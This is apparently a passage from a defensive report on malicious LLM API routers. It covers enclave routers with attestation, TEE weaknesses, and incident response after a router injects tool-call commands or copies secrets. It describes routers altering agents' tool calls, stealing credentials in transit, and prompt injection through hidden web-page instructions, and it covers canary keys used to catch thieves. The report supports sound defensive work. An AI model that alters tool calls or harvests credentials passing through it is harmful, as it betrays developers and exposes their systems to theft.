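1. Get the operator's signed manifest, which contains the source, the build instructions and the expected measurement.
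2. Check that the manifest appears in the public transparency log, a record to which the operator can only add. This makes it hard to show one customer a special version.
3. Review the source. The relay must forward both request and response unchanged, send text only to the listed destinations, and reveal nothing else about the conversation to the host.
4. Build the program from that source and compare the resulting measurement with the one in the manifest. This works only if the build is reproducible, meaning that the same source and instructions always give the same image.
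5. Store the measurement in the sidecar as *m*\*.

If a release contained malware that the public source did not, the user's rebuild would expose it, because the two builds would have different measurements.

Most updates don't require a new review, because billing, scheduling and administration run outside the enclave. A user who doesn't want to rebuild the program can accept a measurement signed by someone they trust, but then depends on that person's review. The user also has to get the sidecar from somewhere other than the operator, since a sidecar that has been tampered with could skip every check.

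Xie and colleagues planted ten faults in the relay to test whether coding agents could do the review. Claude Code found all ten. Codex found eight, missing a mismatch between a destination's host and path, and a fault that let the host control the model named in the request. Neither agent raised a false alarm on the clean version.

This result is encouraging for a program of this size, but ten faults are a small test, and a dishonest author would try harder to hide a fault. The researchers treat the result as a pilot. For this review, the agent also needs a direct connection to its model, not one through the router it is reviewing.

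An enclave running well-reviewed source can still be unsafe if it takes in other data after the measurement. Trail of Bits' *What we learned about TEE security from auditing WhatsApp's Private Inference* (2026) describes an audit of a system in which Meta processes WhatsApp messages inside enclaves, also called trusted execution environments (TEEs). The auditors found 28 issues, eight of them high-severity. In one, the system loaded settings after taking the measurement, so a malicious insider could have used a setting to load hostile code while the attestation remained valid. In another, the attestation lacked a nonce, so an attacker who broke into an enclave once could have reused its attestation document indefinitely.

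Meta fixed both problems before launch. AEGIS already includes a nonce, and the messages between its enclave and the operator's software have only 18 fields, none of which can carry an address or conversation text. But Meta's design was also careful, and outside auditors still found these mistakes, so an enclave router should have an independent audit before anyone relies on it for sensitive work.

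### What the operator can still see and control

AEGIS doesn't hide the length or timing of messages. The operator can see the size of each encrypted piece of a streamed response, which can reveal the lengths of its tokens. Xie and colleagues cite earlier research that reconstructed text from such lengths. A router's operator is unusually well placed to do this because it carries every connection and can use its own accounts to collect matching text for training. Padding each piece to a standard size inside the enclave would help, but the prototype doesn't do this.

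The operator also chooses the account and can delay or refuse any request. If three destinations are permitted, the operator can choose only among those, but AEGIS can't control what a provider shows the account's owner. If the provider stores conversations and lets customers read them, the operator might recover the text. The formal guarantee doesn't cover this because it assumes the provider is honest and protects the text only on its way to the provider.

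AEGIS is also designed for a single operator who hosts the router and owns the provider accounts. In the earlier chain of a reseller, an aggregator and OpenRouter, an enclave at the reseller would protect the text only until it reached the aggregator, which could still read and rewrite everything. One of the three interfaces in the evaluation connects to OpenRouter, which is itself a router, so anyone using that interface still has to trust OpenRouter. Users can at least see where their requests go next, because the source code lists the destinations. Xie and colleagues suggest that an enclave could require attestation from another enclave router before forwarding anything, but the prototype doesn't support this.

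Another risk is that the enclave would accept a false certificate if a certificate authority issued one, because it checks the provider's certificate in the usual way.

### How far to trust the hardware

With Nitro Enclaves, the user also has to trust Amazon, whose hypervisor (the software that runs virtual machines) enforces the isolation and issues the attestation. *SoK* (2025), a study of protected virtual machines in public clouds, excluded Nitro Enclaves because Amazon is both the hardware vendor and the cloud provider. A developer worried about an unknown reseller is still much better off trusting Amazon instead.

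The operator is in a strong position to attack the enclave with software, because in AEGIS the operator controls the virtual machine that hosts it. That machine is the only component with direct access to the enclave, according to Trail of Bits' *A few notes on AWS Nitro Enclaves* (2024). AEGIS's guarantees don't cover side channels, which leak secrets through effects such as timing.

On AMD processors, SEV-SNP protects a virtual machine from the cloud company's software. *AMD SEV-SNP* (2026), an introduction to the technology, says that it "trades trust in many parties for concentrated trust in one", namely AMD, and that its threat model excludes side channels.

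Physical access can defeat some of these protections. SecurityWeek reports that researchers from Purdue University and Georgia Tech extracted secret keys from Intel and AMD systems with a device placed between the processor and its memory. The attack, TEE.fail, can also extract attestation keys, which an attacker could use to produce a valid attestation for a program running outside any enclave. *Physical integrity, attestation, and the state of permissionless TEEs* puts the cost of the attack at $1,000 and the time at 15 minutes.

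This matters a lot for routers because the suspected attacker is the operator, who can open the server if they own it. Attestation from an enclave in a large cloud company's data centre is therefore much better evidence than attestation from one in the operator's own office, and a user should ask where the machine is before relying on it.

### Two other attested gateways

OpenGradient runs the larger gateway in the code-size comparison. Xie and colleagues write that such gateways let the client check only after it has sent its text. OpenGradient's *Private Inference* describes a somewhat stronger arrangement, in which a public registry checks the enclave's attestation in advance, and the client encrypts its request to a key in that registry and verifies a signature on the response. The remaining difference is that OpenGradient's enclave transforms messages. Its attestation shows that the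 expected gateway handled a response, but the user has to review much more code to know what the gateway did to it.

Wang and Tian (2026), in *Evidence-Bound Gateway-Path Provenance for Third-Party LLM Inference*, limit the operator's control over routing. Their client sends a contract with each request that lists the permitted providers, models, accounts and prices, and says when the gateway may switch to a fallback. For example, the contract might require provider A first and allow B only if A times out. The enclave enforces the contract and signs a record of what happened. The client rejects the record if it shows that the gateway went straight to B.

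The design gives users control that AEGIS leaves with the operator, but it puts more work inside the enclave. It has also been tested less with real providers. The prototype completed 30 live requests, all with a single permitted route, and the researchers tested fallback only against simulated services.

### Compared with connecting directly or signing responses

The simplest way to protect tool calls from routers is to connect directly to the provider. This also prevents a router's operator from copying secrets. The developer loses the router's services, such as fallback and a single key for many providers, but some are easy to replace. For example, a developer who only wants a choice of models can open an account with each provider and switch between them in the agent's settings.

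| | Direct connection | Response signing | AEGIS |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who has to cooperate | Nobody else | The provider | The router's operator |
| Whom the user trusts | The provider | The provider and the shim's author | The provider, Amazon, the relay's reviewers and the sidecar's author |
| Altered tool calls | No router to alter them | The shim rejects them | The operator can't make them |
| Secrets in the conversation | The provider sees them | Routers also see them, without added encryption | Hidden from the operator |
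| Several untrusted routers in a row | Not applicable | Protected | Protected only as far as the next router |
| Measured delay per call | None | About 3 ms | About 6 ms for a small request |

The delays come from different experiments, so the difference between 3 and 6 ms means little. It matters more whose cooperation each defense needs. Signing depends on providers, and no major provider is known to sign tool calls. An operator could install AEGIS without a provider's help, but a dishonest operator has no reason to, and an honest one has little reason to take on the extra work unless customers demand it.

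AEGIS is most promising at a company's own gateway, because the company can require its developers to use attestation. An attacker who took over the gateway's administrative functions still couldn't read the conversations. The company couldn't read them at the gateway either, so it would lose central logs of prompts and responses, content filters and conversion between providers' formats. It would have to run any checks it still wanted on the developers' machines.

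An enclave router and provider signatures can also work together. AEGIS forwards every byte unchanged, so it wouldn't break a provider's signature, and the signature would expose changes by any router beyond the enclave. For now, developers who can connect directly to the provider are better off doing so, unless an enclave router's services justify trusting more parties.

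## Finding out afterwards what a router changed or copied

A developer may have used a router for months before something makes them suspect it, such as a news report, an unfamiliar package or an alert about a stolen key. By then, altered commands may have run and other people may have copies of the secrets in the traffic. The developer has to limit the damage before working out what happened.

### The order of work

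1. Stop every auto-approved session and remove the router's address from the agents' settings. Don't use an agent to investigate through the same router, because the router could alter its answers.
2. Preserve the records before cleaning anything up. Copy the agents' transcripts and settings, the shell history and any logs to storage that the affected machines can't change. After its March compromise, LiteLLM told users to remove the malicious file immediately but to keep relevant evidence if their security team was investigating.
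3. List the affected sessions on every machine that used the router, including build servers. If a company's own gateway ran malicious software, the list should cover the whole period when that version was installed.
4. Inspect the commands that ran and the packages they installed. Any download, new package or changed settings file needs a reason connected to the task. Code that the team has already merged from these sessions needs a security review too.
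5. Replace every credential that the router or an altered command could have read.
6. Rebuild any machine that ran a malicious command or one that nobody can explain.

Automated searches can help with the third step. LiteLLM published scripts that search GitHub and GitLab build records for the malicious March versions. By default the scripts check only the current day's jobs, so anyone who ran them later without changing the dates could have got a clean result even if earlier builds had used those versions.

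Replacing credentials is the fifth step because the list of sessions shows which ones to replace, but the most powerful keys should be replaced before the list is complete. The security blog ai.rud.is (2026) describes thieves whose software checks what a stolen key is worth within seconds of taking it. If two people are available, one can start replacing keys while the other preserves the records. Whoever replaces the keys should use a clean machine, since malware on the old one could steal the new keys too.

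Which credentials to replace depends on what the router did. If it only copied traffic, the exposed secrets are those that appeared in prompts, files the agent read and command output. If a malicious command from the router also ran, they include every secret the developer's account could reach on that machine. Nobody can reset the private key of a cryptocurrency wallet, so its owner has to move the funds to a new wallet.

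Replacing an exposed key doesn't shut out an attacker who has already used it to gain another way in. Datadog Security Labs investigated an exposed Amazon Web Services (AWS) key and found that attackers had used it to create new users and set up infrastructure to keep their access. A team whose key was exposed therefore has to check each account for unfamiliar users, keys and permissions added since the exposure.

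Rebuilding is slower than deleting a suspicious file, but deletion works only if the investigator finds everything. HeroDevs, a software support company, includes a clean rebuild in its advice on the March LiteLLM compromise, in which one release left behind a file that ran whenever Python started. The new machine shouldn't reuse the old package cache, which may still contain a substituted package.

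### A log that the router can't reach

The investigation is much easier if a log already exists. Liu and colleagues tested an append-only log, which accepts new entries but doesn't allow anyone to edit or delete old ones. Crosley lists what it records:

- the request
- the response as the agent received it
- the router's address
- details of the TLS connection
- a hash of the raw response

A team that learns of a malicious domain can search this log for every session in which the domain appeared. The team can also find which sessions carried a particular credential.

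Each entry takes about 1.26 KB, so 10,000 entries a day take about 12.6 MB, or 4.6 GB a year. The 1.26 KB figure was measured on synthetic traffic. Real coding sessions may need far more, because a coding agent sends the whole conversation with every request, and 1.26 KB holds only about 1,260 characters. If each request were 1 MB, 10,000 complete copies would take 10 GB a day. Saving each message once, instead of every time the agent repeats it, would avoid most of that storage.

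The log has to be on a separate machine, because an injected command runs with the developer's permissions and could edit or delete a log kept in the developer's folders. The developer's account should be able to add entries to the log and do nothing else. The entries also have to reach it over a connection that doesn't go through the router.

A hash chain, in which each entry includes the hash of the one before, makes later edits detectable. *Agent Flight Recorder* limits this protection to entries written before an attacker takes over, since the attacker can write false ones after that. *AuthGuard-R* (2026), a design for protecting robots controlled by language models, addresses the risk that an attacker deletes the entire log or replaces it with a new chain. It periodically signs the latest hash or sends it to a separate trusted service. A team that does this once an hour could lose up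 to an hour of entries without noticing immediately.

Developers should remove secrets before saving a log entry. Otherwise, anyone who can read the log can use every password the agent has handled. The logging fault that LiteLLM found in March exposed credentials in this way to everyone with access to the monitoring system.

Simply deleting the secrets would make the fifth step harder, because the log would no longer show which credentials had crossed the router. Replacing each secret with a label such as "deployment key 3" keeps that information without saving the key itself. The program should hash the raw response before it removes anything. The saved text may not match that hash, so the program should also log where it made each replacement.

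### Why the log can't prove a change

Fu and colleagues separate three versions of a tool call that matter in an investigation: the response the provider produced, the response the router delivered and the action the agent executed. A local log contains the delivered response, and the machine's own records can show what ran. The log's hash proves that nobody has edited the entry since it was logged, but it can't show whether the router changed the response before it arrived.

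To prove that a router changed a tool call, an investigator needs the provider's record of the original call. A company that connects its own gateway to its own provider account can ask for that record, if the provider still has it. A reseller's customer usually can't, because the provider account belongs to a router's operator. The customer may not even know which account handled the request, and the provider has good reason not to share an account's records with someone who doesn't own it.

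Even with the original, the investigator has to compare the names and arguments of the calls rather than their hashes, because honest routers may reformat a tool call, which changes its hash.

The router may keep records of its own, but they often leave out what an investigator needs. OpenRouter's *Router Metadata* describes a field that can show how the service handled a request, including the provider it chose and any retries. The feature is experimental, and the user has to ask for it with each request, so it can't help with a past session in which nobody did. Cloudflare lets users of its gateway turn off storage of requests and responses while still recording the model, cost and duration. A company that did this could show that a call took place but not what command it contained.

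A router's records also come from the party under suspicion, and a dishonest router could log the altered command as the original. *Agent Flight Recorder* (2026), a proposal for logging what agents do, raises the same objection to AWS logs. Their integrity depends on trusting Amazon, which is a problem when Amazon is a party to the dispute.

Without the provider's record, the local log can still help distinguish payload injection from prompt injection. If the agent read a web page with hidden instructions just before it received a matching command, the model probably followed those instructions. If nothing in the logged conversation leads to the command, the router is more likely to be the source. This isn't proof, because models make mistakes and a router could have added instructions to the request after the local program logged it.

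The log can't reveal copying because, as Wu and colleagues note, a router can store conversations while returning correct answers. Even a team with a perfect log that shows no suspicious commands has to replace the secrets that passed through a router it no longer trusts.

### Canary credentials

A canary credential is a planted key that has no legitimate use, so any attempt to use it is a sign that someone copied it. To test a router, the developer puts the key in a file that the agent will read, then waits for an alert.

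The planted key should not give a thief access to anything. The AWS keys described in Thinkst's *A “Safety Net” for AWS Canarytokens* (2022) have no permissions and belong to an account at Thinkst, the security company that issues them, so they don't expose the defender's own systems. In the case on ai.rud.is, the planted credentials belonged to an AWS role that denied every action. Thieves took credentials in three waves, and two operators made 25 calls with them. AWS refused all 25 and left the defender a timestamped record of what the operators had tried. These thefts didn't involve a router, but the alert would work the same way if a router had stolen the credentials.

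Liu and colleagues planted AWS keys and an Ethereum wallet's private key in traffic through the routers they tested. For 17 of the 400 free routers, someone later used an AWS key that the router had handled. Someone also used the private key sent through one free router to empty the bait wallet, which held under $50. The researchers observed neither outcome with the 28 paid routers.

The AWS result amounts to about 4% of the free routers (95% binomial interval 2.5% to 6.7%), roughly twice as many as injected code. This makes sense because copying is much harder for a customer to notice. Finding no cases among the 28 paid routers is weak evidence that they are safer. If they had the same rate as the free ones, a sample of that size would still contain no cases about 30% of the time (0.9575²⁸ ≈ 0.30).

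More than 17 free routers may have copied credentials. Crosley reports that the researchers counted a key only when it produced later activity on AWS, so they would have missed a thief who saved the key for later or recognised it as bait. Even a key that is used may go unnoticed, because AWS canaries rely mainly on CloudTrail, Amazon's activity log. Tracebit, a company that makes canary credentials, warns that CloudTrail doesn't record every request. An Ethereum canary avoids that gap because anyone can see a transfer on the public blockchain, but its owner has to risk some money.

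Fu and colleagues cite the same study as finding 18 routers that "abuse in-transit credentials". They probably added the router connected to the Ethereum theft to the 17 connected to AWS keys, which is right only if that router wasn't already among the 17. "Abuse" is also stronger than the evidence allows, since a supplier further upstream could have taken the keys.

### Which router copied the key?

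Suppose a developer sends a canary key only along the earlier path of a reseller, an aggregator and OpenRouter, and someone later uses it. The key probably leaked on that path, but any of the three routers, the model's host or an intruder at any of them could have copied it.

Separate keys can narrow this down. Suppose the developer sends a different key along each of three paths:

| Path of the key | Result | What it suggests |
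|---|---|---|
| Reseller A, the aggregator, OpenRouter | Someone uses the key | The leak is somewhere on this path |
| Reseller B, the same aggregator, OpenRouter | Someone uses the key | The leak is probably at the aggregator or beyond |
| OpenRouter directly | Nobody uses the key | The aggregator is the main suspect |

The last row is the weakest, because a thief may not try every key. If a thief tried a random half of the keys they copied, a single key would have a 50% chance of going unused, and five keys would have about a 3% chance of all going unused (0.5⁵). The developer also needs to know that both resellers use the same aggregator, and may have to rely on what the resellers say.

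Different keys can also show how a secret leaked. Wang and Tian put separate markers in the prompt, the response and the provider credential to see which the operator's side of a gateway could read. An ordinary gateway exposed all three. A developer can similarly plant one key in a file the agent reads and another in a file it never opens. If someone uses the key from the unopened file, that suggests a malicious command or other malware took it from the machine, which calls for rebuilding the machine as well as replacing the credentials.

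Records of how a key was used are better evidence about the person who used it than about the router. An AWS guide reconstructs an intrusion from CloudTrail logs by following the same role and IP address from a failed attempt to create a user to a successful request to an AI model about an hour and a half later. The shared role and address link these events, but the address may belong to a rented server, and the person using the key may have bought it from whoever copied it. The key must have been copied before it was used, but possibly long before, so a key used in June may have leaked through a router the developer dropped in March.

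Liu and colleagues faced the same uncertainty with the OpenAI key they leaked on purpose. A developer who accuses a particular reseller on this kind of evidence could easily be wrong. The developer can protect future traffic without knowing which reseller was responsible by leaving the whole path, as long as the replacement doesn't buy from the same suppliers.
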